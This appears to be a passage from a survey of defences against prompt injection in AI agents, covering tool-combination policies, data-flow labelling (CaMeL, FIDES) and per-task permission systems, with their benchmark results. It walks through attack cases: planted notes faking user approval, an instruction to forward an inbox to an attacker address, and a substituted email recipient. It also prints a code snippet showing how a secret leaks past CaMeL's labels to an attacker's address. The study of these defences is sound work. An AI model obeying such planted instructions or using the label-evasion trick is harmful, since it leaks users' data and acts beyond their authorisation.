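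If any tool bans sending data out, the ban applies to the whole session, which also takes the strictest setting of each control. DSCC then rejects sets of tools that break its rules. For example, it does not allow a tool that sends data out in a session rated Confidential or higher, so an agent cannot have both a Confidential database tool and a tool that uploads files to an outside service.

Checking the tools in pairs would not always be enough. Suppose one tool may run in zones A and B, another in B and C, and a third in A and C. Each pair shares a zone, but no zone is common to all three, so DSCC rejects the set.

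Adding a tool can never loosen the combined policy, so Schneider and colleagues argue that a reviewer who has approved a set of tools needs to consider only what a new one contributes. This is true of the policy, but a new tool also gives the agent more ways to use the old ones, and the policy restricts only what its labels describe. DSCC's labels cover secrecy but not whether content is trustworthy. DSCC lets an agent have both file-reading and file-writing tools, so a malicious instruction in one file could lead the agent to overwrite another.

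DSCC has two modes. In clearance mode, the default, every tool must have the session's highest sensitivity rating. An Internal planning tool cannot work with a Confidential database, even if no data leaves the company. Taint mode drops this requirement but keeps the limits on sending data out. The team tested every combination of 32 tools governed by 16 policies:

| Combination | Total | Blocked in clearance mode | Blocked in taint mode |
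|---|---|---|---|
| Pairs of policies | 120 | 95 (79.2%) | 51 (42.5%) |
| Sets of three policies | 560 | 535 (95.5%) | 339 (60.5%) |
| Ordered pairs of tools | 992 | 704 (71.0%) | 322 (32.5%) |
| Sets of three tools | 4,960 | 4,499 (90.7%) | 2,350 (47.4%) |

These rates depend on how the team labelled its tools. They do not measure how many of the blocked combinations people would want, or how many attacks DSCC would stop. But in the online shop, the email policy conflicts with all 15 others in both modes, including those for planning and reading the company wiki. An agent could not look up an order and email the answer in the same session.

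In a further phase, during the session, DSCC checks the sensitivity of each file or record as the agent opens it and rates the session at the highest level so far. If a later call would send data out in violation of the rules, DSCC ends the session. In one scenario, an agent reads public documents and product prices, then queries salaries. DSCC ends the session when the agent tries to upload something to an outside service. This would stop the salary leak even without an attacker, which the three simpler rules would not.

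The team demonstrated this phase on only three scenarios. Under its published policies, DSCC should have rejected all three before they started, because each combined a Confidential file or database tool with one that sends data out. One was a harmless agent that posted a summary of public information to the messaging service Slack. The scenarios show that checks during a session can distinguish harmless uses from harmful ones, but DSCC's strict check at the start would block both.

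Schneider and colleagues accept that DSCC makes agents less general, but argue that a company can notice a wrongly blocked task and correct the policy, whereas it cannot take back leaked data. DSCC helps by reporting which tool and control caused a rejection. They also suggest dividing long tasks into smaller chains with separate policies. This works if the parts do not need to share secrets, but the shop's mail agent needs the order details from the database agent. The mail agent cannot send those details while they are labelled Confidential, and DSCC no longer protects them once the label is removed.

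The policies also need updating as tools change. Schneider and colleagues propose that each tool's developers write its policy, since they know the tool best, and that a central security team set minimum requirements, since developers have a reason to be permissive. This arrangement suits a large company better than someone who installs public MCP servers at home.

### Checking what each call carries

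*AGATE* (Zhang, Cheng and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that lets an agent hold a dangerous set of tools and checks the agent's calls as they happen. The system runs in the host and checks who authorised a call and where the data in it came from.

Authorisation can come from the company's rules or from a user's approval in the host. By default, an approval lasts 30 minutes and covers up to three calls with exactly the same tool and arguments. Text that the agent reads cannot authorise anything. In one test, a planted note claimed that the user had permanently approved refunds, but AGATE refused the refund call when no tools had advance permission.

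AGATE traces data by storing fingerprints of 12-character pieces of the text an agent reads, along with their sources. When a call would carry text across a protected boundary, AGATE looks for matching pieces and applies the company's rule for that source and destination. An agent could therefore read the salary file and still email the supplier about a delivery date, but AGATE could block a message that quoted the file.

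The drawback of this flexibility is that a translation or paraphrase may not match. In a test with a simulated mailbox, a planted note contained the false claim that the user had authorised permanently deleting messages. AGATE blocked a call because of where its data came from, but the agent changed the arguments and then reached the deletion tool. DSCC does not compare text, so it is not vulnerable to rewording.

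Matching also blocks some legitimate copying. AGATE blocked at least one call in six of 11 harmless file-processing scenarios. Of the eight blocked calls, five reused text for legitimate reasons, two involved similar file names, and one correctly matched a data rule. Zhang and colleagues did not measure how many tasks failed as a result, or how much AGATE slows an agent down.

The shop's agent would have the same difficulty, since a useful reply repeats details from the database. The shop could permit this, but a rule that allowed any database text in replies would also allow another customer's address. AGATE also has less control on some hosts. In the tests with the coding agent OpenCode, AGATE could only record violations.

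### What users will give up

Willison thinks the ability to send data out is generally the easiest of the three functions to remove. Lockdown Mode, which OpenAI began offering to personal ChatGPT accounts in June 2026, takes this approach by limiting outgoing network requests that could carry data to an attacker. A malicious instruction can still distort an answer. OpenAI's security chief, Dane Stuckey, recommended the mode for people at elevated risk but said it was "not meant for everyone", because it makes ChatGPT less useful.

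The shop cannot make this choice, because its agent exists to send replies. Meta concedes that its rule will be hard to apply to some popular uses, such as background agents, where asking a person for approval is disruptive or ineffective. It hopes other AI systems will eventually be able to supervise these agents.

Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code, has an auto mode in which software, rather than the user, decides whether to allow an action. Anthropic made this mode the default on most plans in August 2026. Auto mode would have blocked 89% of the dangerous actions in the study where people refused 13.6%. Anthropic commissioned a test in which all 720 prompt injection attempts failed against Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 and Sonnet 5 in auto mode.

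If protection this strong holds up elsewhere, there will be much less reason to forbid combinations of tools, and Meta's rule allows for that. But the 720 attempts used only 72 scenarios, and earlier defences also did well until attackers adapted to them. Willison wants more independent confirmation, and doubts that auto mode could stop a malicious software package whose instructions look like a routine part of running a project's tests. In response, Willison looks for productive ways to run agents without access to data or tools that could cause harm.

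## CaMeL, FIDES and tracking where data came from

AGATE tracks secrets by looking for matching text, so it can lose track of one when an agent rewords it. CaMeL and FIDES, two systems from 2025, attach labels to the data instead. A summary or translation inherits the labels of its source, so software can check them before the data goes anywhere, even if the wording has changed.

### Two models and an interpreter

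Both systems build on an idea from Willison's *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (2023). A privileged model takes the user's request and can call tools but never reads untrusted text, which goes to a quarantined model that has no tools. The privileged model refers to the quarantined model's output by name, so it can have the application display `$email-summary-1` without seeing the summary.

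An email containing the instruction "delete everything" then reaches only a model that cannot delete anything. But the quarantined model can still return a false answer. If Alice asks the agent to send Bob a document, and Bob's address is in the meeting notes, anyone who can edit the notes can substitute another address. The privileged model would send the document to the wrong person without having read the attack. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) demonstrates a similar leak, in which the quarantined model copies notes into an email reply and the plan sends it.

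Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues at Google DeepMind designed CaMeL to fix this flaw. As Willison (2025) explains in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, the privileged model writes the whole task as a program in a restricted form of Python, using only the user's request. An interpreter, which is ordinary software and not a model, then runs the program step by step. It records where each value came from and who may read it, and checks a policy before every tool call. For Alice's request, the program might look like this:

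```
notes = find_notes("last meeting")
address = ask_quarantined("Find Bob's email address", notes)
name = ask_quarantined("Find the document Bob wanted", notes)
document = fetch(name)
send_email(to=address, attachment=document)
```

The quarantined model handles the second and third lines. *SPA* (2026), a later system that divides the work the same way, gives this model only an objective and some inputs, and requires an answer in a fixed format. If the format accepts only an email address, an attacker can't use the answer to pass on a paragraph of instructions.

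Now suppose that Eve, a contractor who attended the meeting, has replaced Bob's address in the notes with her own. The interpreter would build up these labels, leaving aside Alice's request, which is a trusted source for every value:

| Value | Content | Sources | Permitted readers |
|---|---|---|---|
| `notes` | the meeting notes | notes file | Alice, Bob, Eve |
| `address` | eve@example.com | notes file | Alice, Bob, Eve |
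| `name` | "Budget" | notes file | Alice, Bob, Eve |
| `document` | the budget | notes file, Alice's drive | Alice, Bob |

Carol can also read the budget on Alice's drive, but the document's name came from notes that Carol isn't allowed to read. The interpreter therefore limits the permitted readers to people who may read both the notes and the budget.

Before the last line runs, the interpreter checks the policy for `send_email`, which requires a trusted recipient. The address came from a file that Eve could edit, and Eve is not allowed to read the budget, so the interpreter blocks the message or asks Alice. If the notes had contained Bob's real address, the policy could have allowed the message because Bob is one of Alice's known contacts.

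CaMeL restricts combinations of calls, because each value carries its history into the next call. It also tracks values through calculations, which a checker that monitors only tool calls can miss. If a program adds up ten salaries, CaMeL's interpreter does the addition itself, so the total keeps the restrictions on the salary files.

These labels are called capabilities in CaMeL, but they are metadata and grant no rights. A classical capability lets its holder use a resource, whereas a CaMeL program can hold a document and still be unable to send it.

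### How FIDES labels an agent's context

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, a system from Microsoft. Its planning model chooses one tool call at a time, like an ordinary agent, instead of writing the whole program first, while FIDES labels the data the model reads.

Each label has two parts. Integrity is either trusted or untrusted, and confidentiality lists the people who may read the data. When FIDES combines data from several sources, it keeps the stricter value of each part:

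- Trusted data combined with untrusted data is untrusted.
- If {A, B, C} may read one document and {B, C, D} may read another, then {A, B, C} ∩ {B, C, D} = {B, C} may read anything derived from both.

A model's output gets the combined label of everything in its context, because FIDES cannot determine which parts the model used. FIDES applies two kinds of policy. One blocks a consequential call, such as a payment, if untrusted data influenced it. The other allows data to be sent only to people permitted to read it.

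These rules are very restrictive on their own. After an agent reads one email from a stranger, its whole context is untrusted and it can no longer make a payment, even one the user requested. FIDES avoids much of this by hiding data selectively. If part of a tool's result has a stricter label than the context, FIDES stores that part in a variable and shows the planning model only the variable's name. For example, the model might see an email's date but not its body. The model can pass the variable to another tool, have a quarantined model answer a question about it, or inspect the contents and accept the stricter label for its context.

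Costa and colleagues give the example of a user who asks the agent to check three emails for a meeting request and, if there is one, add the meeting to the calendar:

1. The agent reads the emails, and FIDES stores their contents in a variable.
2. A quarantined model answers whether they contain a meeting request, with only yes or no allowed.
3. The planning model inspects the answer.
4. If it is yes, the quarantined model extracts the date, time and participants into a second variable.
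5. The planning model calls the calendar tool with that variable.

FIDES labels the yes-or-no answer as untrusted but also records that it can carry only one bit of information. A policy can allow this small influence because one bit cannot carry a new instruction. A stranger could still get a false meeting into the calendar, but could not make the agent forward the mailbox.

### Results on AgentDojo

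*AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024), the standard benchmark for these defences, simulates an office workspace, the messaging service Slack, a travel agency and a bank. It has 97 user tasks and 27 attacker goals. In the bank, for instance, a user might ask the agent to pay a bill stored in a file, while planted text tells it to send money to the attacker. Pairing each user task with every attacker goal in the same setting gives 629 tests.

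The benchmark measures how many tasks an agent completes with and without attacks, and how often the attacker succeeds. Ordinary code checks whether the money moved or the email went out, because planted text that misled the agent might also mislead a model judging the outcome. The benchmark has since grown to over 900 combinations, according to *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026).

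Costa and colleagues tested FIDES with GPT-4o, a model from 2024. The table gives the percentage of tasks completed without attacks, and the number of attacks that succeeded in separate runs after the team had removed cases that the benchmark misjudged:

| Agent | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| No defence | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 | 152 |
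| Labels and policies, no hiding | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 | 0 |
| FIDES without policy checks | 63.5 | 50.0 | 65.0 | 63.8 | 21 |
| FIDES | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 | 0 |

Averaged over the four settings, the agent completed 84% of the tasks undefended, 42% with labels and policies alone, and 50% with FIDES. Selective hiding recovered only some of the loss. It worked better with o1, a reasoning model from the same year, which made fewer mistakes with the variables. With o1 and no policy checks, FIDES was only 6.3% behind the undefended agent. FIDES also takes more time and tokens because each question to the quarantined model adds a turn. The team had not tried to make it efficient.

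Two teams reran CaMeL on newer models and found that it completed fewer tasks with its policies on. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, ran the 16 banking tasks three times each. With the policies on, CaMeL completed 18 of 48 runs with both GPT-5.2 and MiMo-v2.5. With them off, it completed 32 and 34 respectively. The policies blocked every attack in the runs that finished. Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026), in *Language-Based Agent Control*, used the 21 Slack tasks. Across four models, CaMeL completed 13 to 17 tasks without policies and 4 to 6 with them. The division into two models stayed in place in both conditions, so the policies themselves caused these losses. However, both sets of tasks are small, and different policies would give different results.

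AgentDojo's standard attacks are no longer much of a test of a defence on recent models. The four models that Zhou and colleagues used, including Claude Opus 4.8 and GPT 5.4, resisted all 105 Slack attacks even without policies. The team therefore simulated the worst case on its own system, ELBA. Whenever one of the agent's subagents read an injected instruction, the team replaced that subagent's task with the attacker's. Up to 42% of the 735 attacks succeeded without policies, depending on the model. None succeeded with policies, but the number of user tasks completed fell from 494–558 to 294–351.

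Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, argue that such comparisons exaggerate how much defences reduce an agent's usefulness. A blocked action counts as a failure for the defended agent, but the undefended agent is allowed to take actions that many real products would ask a person to approve. In the team's tests on AgentDojo with the model o3-mini, an ordinary agent that had to ask before every consequential action needed about 48 approvals for the tasks it completed, while FIDES needed about 19. With no approvals allowed, the ordinary agent completed 24% of the tasks and FIDES 50%. Prudentia, the team's extension of FIDES, reached 59% by telling the planning model about the labels and policies so that it could avoid actions that FIDES would block.

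This is a good argument for companies that now require approval for everything important. But people also use approvals to catch a model's own mistakes, and a label check may let those mistakes through. The security results also assume that people would refuse every attack they are shown, which Anthropic's study of developers gives little reason to expect.

### What the systems guarantee

In CaMeL, text in the data cannot add a step to the program, because the privileged model writes the program before the system reads any of the data. An attacker can change only the values in the program, and the policies restrict where those values can go. FIDES lets the agent change its plan as it works but stops any call whose labels violate a policy. Neither guarantee depends on a model recognising an attack.

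These systems depend on accurate labels, suitable policies and trusted tools. Both teams assume that the user, the planning model and the tools' code are trustworthy. Kolluri and colleagues also exclude attacks hidden in tool descriptions, which is a large exclusion for MCP because each server supplies its own descriptions.

FIDES stops secret data from flowing directly to people who aren't allowed to read it, but it does not stop them from inferring some of it from the agent's actions. For example, if an agent sends Bob a routine reminder only when a salary is above some figure, Bob can infer that the salary is above that figure, even though the reminder contains nothing secret. Costa and colleagues accept this gap because closing it would essentially mean forbidding every publicly visible action after the agent has read a secret.

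CaMeL has a strict mode that also labels values according to the conditions that led to them. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL's tracking can still miss a condition when the program skips a branch. A simplified program shows how:

```
low = True
rich = True
if balance > 1000000:
    low = False
if low:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("mallory@example.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is above a million, `low` becomes false and gets a secret label. The program then skips `rich = False`, so the interpreter never labels `rich` as secret. The last condition appears to depend only on public data, and the program sends the email. An attacker would struggle to exploit this directly, because the planning model writes the program without reading the attacker's text. But CaMeL's labels can still be wrong. Garby and colleagues built a replacement language, LLMbda, with a computer-checked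 proof that rules out such leaks.

Whether FIDES prevents the accidental leak of a salary file depends on how an administrator combines its two policies. In the tests by Kolluri and colleagues, a tool that sends data out has to satisfy only one of them. An agent that misunderstands its task might email the company's own salary file, which is trusted, to a supplier. FIDES would allow this because no untrusted data influenced the decision. If the administrator requires both policies, FIDES blocks the message, even if the agent has summarised the file. But it also blocks Alice when she deliberately sends a document to someone who could not read it before.

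### When the data has to decide the next step

CaMeL loses generality mainly because it has to write the plan in advance. A user who says "do the tasks on my to-do list" has not said what the tasks are, so the privileged model cannot write a program for them. Costa and colleagues classify about 43% of AgentDojo's Slack tasks, 44% of its banking tasks and only 5% of its workspace tasks as ones where the agent has to see the data before it can choose its actions. A benchmark made up mostly of workspace tasks would therefore overstate how well fixed plans work for other tasks.

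AgentDyn, a newer benchmark described in *StepGuard* (2026), has longer tasks in shopping, software development and daily life, and includes helpful instructions from third parties. *An AI Agent Execution Environment to Safeguard User Data* (2026) reports that CaMeL completed none of these tasks, and attributes this to the tasks requiring work that goes beyond the first prompt. *Twin Agent* (2026) makes the same point about software engineering, where an agent has to look at the results of its changes and revise its approach.

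One response is to plan for every possibility. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) adapted CaMeL to agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen and clicking. The privileged model cannot see the screen, so it writes branches for whatever might appear, such as a cookie banner or a login page. The average plan had 213 lines and 40 branches, compared with 52 lines and four branches on AgentDojo. The agents kept up to 57% of the performance of leading models. An attacker still cannot add a branch, but can mislead the model that reads the screen into choosing the wrong one.

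Zhou and colleagues instead let the agent read data before writing its next piece of code, so it doesn't need a complete plan. Their system, ELBA, checks each piece before it runs. An agent that reads untrusted data can continue working, but it keeps only the privileges of that data's source. With policies on, ELBA completed roughly twice as many Slack tasks as CaMeL.

Another option is endorsement, in which someone marks untrusted data as trusted. In Prudentia, the user does this. If a colleague's email contains a to-do list with ten items, the user can endorse the email once instead of approving ten separate actions. This saves nine interruptions, but if the user endorses a malicious email by mistake, the attacker can have all ten actions carried out.

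Garby and colleagues let the planning model make endorsements in its program, before it has seen any outside data. With Qwen3.7-plus, their agent completed 36 of 48 banking runs with endorsement and 30 without. Across three models, attacks succeeded in only two of 1,296 runs. In both, the user had asked the agent to read a file and pay as it instructed, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a false payment request. Labels cannot separate a genuine bill from a false one in the same file, so without endorsement the agent would have blocked both.

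Attackers can also do harm through data alone, without causing any new action. Costa and colleagues point out that an email could get the quarantined model to return an empty summary, which the agent would send on as planned. In a test in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026), an agent booked the hotel its user had chosen but also quoted reviews in which an attacker had recommended a different one. A policy could require everything in a message to come from trusted sources, but then the agent could not summarise email from strangers.

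### Who writes the labels and policies

CaMeL's developers acknowledge that users have to write and update security policies. This worries Willison because, after two decades of working in application security, he already has enough trouble with such policies. Asking the user whenever a policy gives no clear answer would bring back approval fatigue.

Costa and colleagues needed only three general policies for all of AgentDojo, so the rules may be manageable. The labels took more judgement because the benchmark did not supply any. The team assumed that an email's permitted readers were its sender and recipients, although someone might have shared it more widely. If any attack in the benchmark used a field, such as the body of an email, they labelled that field untrusted everywhere.

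Such broad labels block harmless work. In one task, the user wanted a password reset link from the mailbox, but FIDES failed because it could not distinguish a trusted sender from a stranger. Fixing this requires more precise labels, which are feasible because mail servers can authenticate many senders. In another task, the agent listed all the Slack channels even though the user had already named the right one, which made its context untrusted. Avoiding this requires a planner that accounts for whether each step will make the context untrusted, as in Prudentia.

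A system can also release one value for one purpose. In Santos-Grueiro's *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (2026), an error log may supply the path of a file that needs fixing, but it may not influence which tool the agent uses. Someone has to write trusted code to check each such release. Costa and colleagues also mention upgrading a document to trusted after an injection detector passes it, but they warn against relying too heavily on detectors, which can miss attacks.

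In May 2026 Microsoft added FIDES to its Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents. According to Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026), FIDES passes labels through tool calls automatically, so developers don't have to build the tracking themselves. But the tracking is only as reliable as the initial labels, and the proposals for trust and secrecy labels in MCP are not yet part of the standard.

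### PACE and untrusted tool descriptions

Li, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *PACE*, address a threat that CaMeL and FIDES largely leave out, malicious tool descriptions and skills. Their example is a mail skill that comes in two versions with identical code. The instructions in one tell the model to fill in a fixed template, while those in the other tell it to copy a password into the message. A reviewer who examines only the code and the interface cannot tell them apart. PACE, released in October 2026, therefore checks each call immediately before it runs, when the actual message is available:

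1. It freezes the call's arguments so that the agent cannot change them after the check.
2. It compares the arguments with data from earlier in the task and adds the call to a graph of where that data has gone.
3. It looks for a path to an unsafe action from a secret or from a source that an attacker could have influenced.
4. Separately, it compares the call's effects with the authority in the user's request, including the resources, arguments and budget that the request covers. Text from tools or the model cannot extend this authority.
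5. It allows, blocks or repairs the call and records the outcome.

PACE detects a secret after some kinds of re-encoding but, like AGATE, can miss one that the agent has paraphrased, translated or split up. The authority check may still stop the leak, since even a paraphrased salary file should not go to a supplier the user never mentioned.

Li and colleagues tested PACE on eight benchmarks with three families of models. It had the lowest attack success rate in 62 of 79 comparisons and tied for the lowest in another 14. Agents' task completion rates were at most three percentage points lower with PACE than without a defence. This is a much smaller loss than CaMeL's or FIDES's, although the tests used different tasks and rules. In a small search for attacks adapted to PACE, no attack succeeded against any of the 30 targets, but a true success rate of nearly 10% could still produce that result.

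The formal guarantees apply to a stricter version than the one in these tests. The stricter version requires the final call to break every unsafe path in the graph and pass the authority check. The tested version can restore a call that the graph check blocked if the authority check accepts it, and it can repair a call without checking it again. The low overhead was therefore measured on a version that the proof does not cover. The team switched off parts of PACE in 1,167 paired cases and found that most of the protection came from comparing a call's effects with what the user had authorised.

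## Progent, PORTICO, IntentCap and permissions for one task

Like PACE, several systems compare an agent's calls with what the user has authorised. They try to give the agent only the permissions its current task requires. This is difficult because a person or program has to work out what the task requires, often before the agent has done enough of the task to discover what it needs.

### Progent's rules for tool calls

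Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, describe a system that checks every tool call against a list of rules. Each rule allows or forbids one tool and can set conditions on its arguments. For example:

`allow send_slack_msg when to = "alice"`

This lets the agent send `alice` Slack messages with any text. Rules can also use comparisons, lists of permitted values and text patterns. If an "allow" rule and a "forbid" rule both match a call, the "forbid" rule takes precedence. Progent also blocks any call that no rule allows. By default, it sends the agent the reason for blocking a call so that the agent can try something else.

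A language model writes the rules for each task and revises them as the agent works. In the main example, a user asks an agent to carry out the to-do list in a particular email:

1. From the request alone, the model writes a rule that allows only a search for that email.
2. The to-do list asks for a summary of the user's recent emails, posted to the user's own Slack account. The model proposes rules for reading email, looking up the user's Slack name and sending Slack messages. These additions need approval.
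3. The agent learns that the Slack name is `alice`. The model tightens the Slack rule to the one above, which needs no approval.
4. One of the recent emails contains a planted instruction to forward the inbox to eve@evil.com. If it misleads the model into proposing a rule for sending email, that rule needs approval too. Without it, Progent blocks the message.
5. The agent posts the summary to Slack.

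Progent uses an SMT solver, a program that checks logical formulas, to decide which rule changes need approval. If the proposed rules allow only calls that the current rules already allow, Progent applies the change. Otherwise it asks for approval. An agent's permissions therefore cannot expand without approval, even if an attacker has misled the model that writes the rules. Companies, developers and users can also write permanent rules that the model cannot override.

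Progent's rules in force depend on what the agent has learned so far, but each rule applies to a single call, and Progent does not track data. It can stop the agent from reading a salary file that the task does not require. If the task requires both reading the file and emailing a supplier, Progent cannot prevent the agent from sending the salary data to that supplier.

### What Progent's tests measured

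With GPT-4o, Progent reduced the attack success rate on AgentDojo from 39.9% to 1.0%, and on another benchmark, ASB, from 70.3% to 3.9%. The agent completed about as many tasks as without a defence. With Claude Sonnet 4, which was already more resistant, the rate on AgentDojo fell from 6.8% to 0.5%.

In these tests, Progent automatically approved every proposed expansion to simulate a careless user, so the solver's guarantee had no effect on the results. Attack success rates were low because the model mostly wrote good rules, even after reading attackers' text. Three kinds of attack meant to corrupt the rules raised the success rate only slightly. This is good evidence about the model tested, but another model might write worse rules.

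Much of the protection came from the first set of rules, which the model writes before the agent has read anything an attacker could control. When Progent kept those rules unchanged throughout the task, 2.5% of attacks succeeded. No attacks succeeded when a person reviewed the first rules and every expansion of them, but the test assumed the reviewer would never approve a malicious address or unrestricted payments.

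Shi and colleagues expect approvals to be rare because only 6% of the rule changes were expansions, though that is a share of changes, not of tasks. The team had permanently allowed harmless read-only tools on AgentDojo, which probably avoided many approval requests. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) warns that hostile text in a tool's result may cause Progent to relax its rules. The solver can detect the relaxation, but someone still has to decide whether it is legitimate. In the example, the genuine to-do list and the planted instruction both arrived by email.

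Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao (2026), in *AGENTCAP*, found a larger loss of usefulness with Progent. In tests on AgentDojo, GPT-4o completed about 81% of the tasks with no defence, 78% with their system, AgentCap, and 68% with Progent. Attackers succeeded about equally often against the two defences. Progent's model often restricted arguments to the values it expected from the request, which blocked legitimate calls with other values.

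AgentCap issues a short-lived token for each approved call. Under its banking policy, for example, a token covers one payment and expires after 30 seconds, and trusted information must support the choice of recipient. AgentCap can also forbid an agent from holding certain permissions together. But people wrote its policies after studying the benchmark's tools and tasks, while Progent had to produce rules from each request. A company that uses agents for a few known jobs could prepare policies this way, but the user of a general assistant could not. Each figure also comes from a single run.

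### PORTICO and the second file

A permission can outlast the reason for granting it. *Lingering Authority* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) presents PORTICO, a reference monitor for coding agents that grants extra access for part of a task and then revokes it.

PORTICO needs a task contract, written before the agent starts. In the main example, a programmer wants an optional timeout setting in `src/api.py` to carry through to a second file, `src/serialization.py`. In simplified form, the contract is:

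```
At the start:  read and write src/api.py and its test
               run the test
On request:    read and write src/serialization.py
               until the tests pass or the subtask ends
Never:         read notes/packaging.md
               change requirements.txt
               use the network
```

The task then goes as follows:

1. The agent starts with the API file, its test and the command that runs the test.
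2. It tries to read the packaging notes, and PORTICO refuses.
3. It requests access to the serialization file. The contract allows this, so PORTICO creates handles for reading and writing the file, which the agent can use from its next step.
4. The agent reads and edits the file through these handles.
5. The tests pass. PORTICO cancels the handles and removes them from the options it gives the agent.
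6. The agent tries an old handle again, and PORTICO rejects it.

The handles are capabilities in the security sense, like Capsicum's file descriptors. PORTICO ties each one to a task, a file, a kind of access and one grant, so a model cannot use a handle after the grant ends, even if it still has the text. By contrast, an MCP token with a scope such as `files:write` normally covers every file in the scope until the token expires.

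PORTICO relies on trusted events to determine when a grant ends, such as the result of a test that PORTICO itself launched or a decision by an authenticated person. The agent cannot extend its access by claiming that it still needs the file, or end a grant by saying it has finished.

### Ending access after a subtask

To test the effect of cancelling access, Santos-Grueiro compared PORTICO with a version that made the same grants at the same moments but never revoked them. Both versions completed all ten runs and made the same decisions until the subtask ended. When the agent then tried to reuse its old access, PORTICO rejected all ten attempts and the other version allowed all ten. In six scripted cases where the agent tried to write to a file with an old handle, PORTICO allowed none of the forbidden writes and the other version allowed all six.

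The results were also 0 of 6 and 6 of 6 when the model Qwen3-Coder 30B received a misleading instruction to reuse an old handle. These cases covered changes to files and version-control data, as well as network requests.

The samples are tiny, but the outcome was almost inevitable, because a system that never cancels handles will accept old ones. The tests confirm that PORTICO's cancellation works, but they do not measure how often an agent would misuse leftover access in ordinary work.

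Yu, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *CreepScope*, give a simple way to count this excess access. Suppose an agent has to read a record, change a setting and send a message, and each step requires one permission. The table gives the number of unnecessary permissions the agent has at each step:

| When the agent gets permissions | Read | Change | Send | Total |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| All at the start | 2 | 2 | 2 | 6 |
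| Each when first needed, then kept | 0 | 1 | 2 | 3 |
| Each for its own step only | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |

Delaying a permission until the agent needs it avoids granting it too early, but the agent keeps it after the need has passed unless the system revokes it. In a simulated mail task, an agent using the small model Qwen2 7B sent its one approved message, then received a planted delivery receipt containing an instruction to send another to an outsider. The agent sent the second message in all nine runs where it still had permission to send, and in none of the three where the permission had been revoked. It completed the legitimate task in every run. However, the system that revoked the permission used an answer key listing what each step required, which a real system would not have.

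PORTICO has no such key, and mistakes in the contract can make tasks fail. In one group of coding tasks, it completed 161 of 185 runs, compared with 180 for a fixed list of allowed tools. Its success rate was only 21% without extra grants, so requests for access prevented most failures. In a supplementary test on real software projects, PORTICO completed 31 of 42 cases, while a version that did not revoke access completed all 42. Some contracts ended access too soon or provided no trusted way to reopen it, and sometimes the agent did not ask again.

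PORTICO recorded no violations of its contracts in the main tests. But each contract was used both to set the rules and to score the results, so this shows that PORTICO enforced the contracts, not that the contracts were right. When Santos-Grueiro deliberately added the packaging notes to a contract's permitted files, PORTICO let the agent read them.

Revocation also does not erase what the agent has read. After PORTICO closes a file, the file's contents remain in the model's context, and the agent can copy them into a message if it has permission to send one.

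### IntentCap and the owner of each field

An agent can make a call that the task requires but give it a harmful argument. *LLM Agent Capabilities Should Follow Task Intent and Context Source* (Zheng, Zhang and Mao, 2026) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to extract tables from two PDFs, save them as spreadsheets and create one GitHub issue in the repository `org/proj`. A PDF contains a hidden instruction to use `attacker/repo` instead. The task requires the issue-creating tool, and both repositories are on GitHub, so allowing only that tool and that website would not stop the attack.

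Their system, IntentCap, divides the information an agent receives into four sources and lets each supply only certain fields:

| Source | What it may supply | In the PDF task |
|---|---|---|
| User's request | Goal, selected objects, destinations, approvals | The two PDFs and `org/proj` |
| Workflow instructions, such as a skill | Procedure | Extract, save, report |
| Tool definition | Form of the call and its credentials | The arguments for creating an issue |
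| Results and files | Observed values | The contents of the tables |

Before each action, a language model proposes a lease, a short-lived permission for that action. For the GitHub issue, the lease contains the repository name copied from the user's request and a record of where in the request it appeared. The text of the issue can come from the PDFs. The lease covers one issue and expires after use.

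Ordinary software then checks the lease. If the hidden text has misled the model into proposing `attacker/repo`, the software refuses because nothing in the user's request supports that name. The same check catches innocent mistakes, such as the model reading a table heading as the repository's name. CaMeL's rule for sending email similarly required a trusted recipient, but IntentCap applies the idea to every field.

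Leases can only narrow what the user authorised. In this task, a lease could cover one of the two PDFs but not a third, and a subagent would get less authority than the agent that delegated the work. A skill cannot add a destination or approve an action on the user's behalf.

Field ownership does not keep data secret. If the user selects a confidential PDF and names a public repository, the confidential figures may go into the issue, because the PDF is a permitted source for the issue's text. The ownership rule controls who chooses the repository, but a separate rule would be needed to control whether that repository may receive the figures.

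Zheng and colleagues tested the checker on 3,746 security-sensitive events from AgentDojo and three other benchmarks, and it accepted none that it should have refused. On legitimate actions, it passed 2,554 of 2,556 applicable checks. When they merged the four sources into a single trusted one, the checker wrongly accepted 3,593 of the 3,823 events it should have refused, or 94%. In the two-source merges they report, it wrongly accepted between 43% and 50%.

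The separation clearly mattered for these events. But the team replayed recorded or constructed events through the checker, so the test did not measure how many tasks a working agent would complete or how many attacks against it would succeed. The 94% also depends on which attacks the benchmarks contain. The team has not yet tested against attackers who try to corrupt the labels or the proposed leases.

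### Stating a task's needs in advance

All three systems need a description of the task. PORTICO uses a contract written beforehand, IntentCap takes destinations and approvals from the user's request, and Progent has a model infer the rules and revise them. Tasks listed in an email are difficult for all three, as they are for CaMeL. A PORTICO-style contract would have to cover those tasks in advance, and IntentCap would not normally accept a destination that came from the email. Progent can add the missing permissions, but only after someone approves them.

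Coding has the same problem. A user who reports that a program crashes does not know which file contains the fault, so the agent has to find it. A contract that covers every file gives little protection, but one that covers only the likely files may keep the agent from reaching the faulty one.

One option is to predict the limits at the start. CapScope, described in *Authority Is Not a String* (2026), sets the maximum permissions for a coding task before any model reads the repository or any tool output. This prevents planted text from influencing the prediction, but it also means the prediction can't use helpful information in the code.

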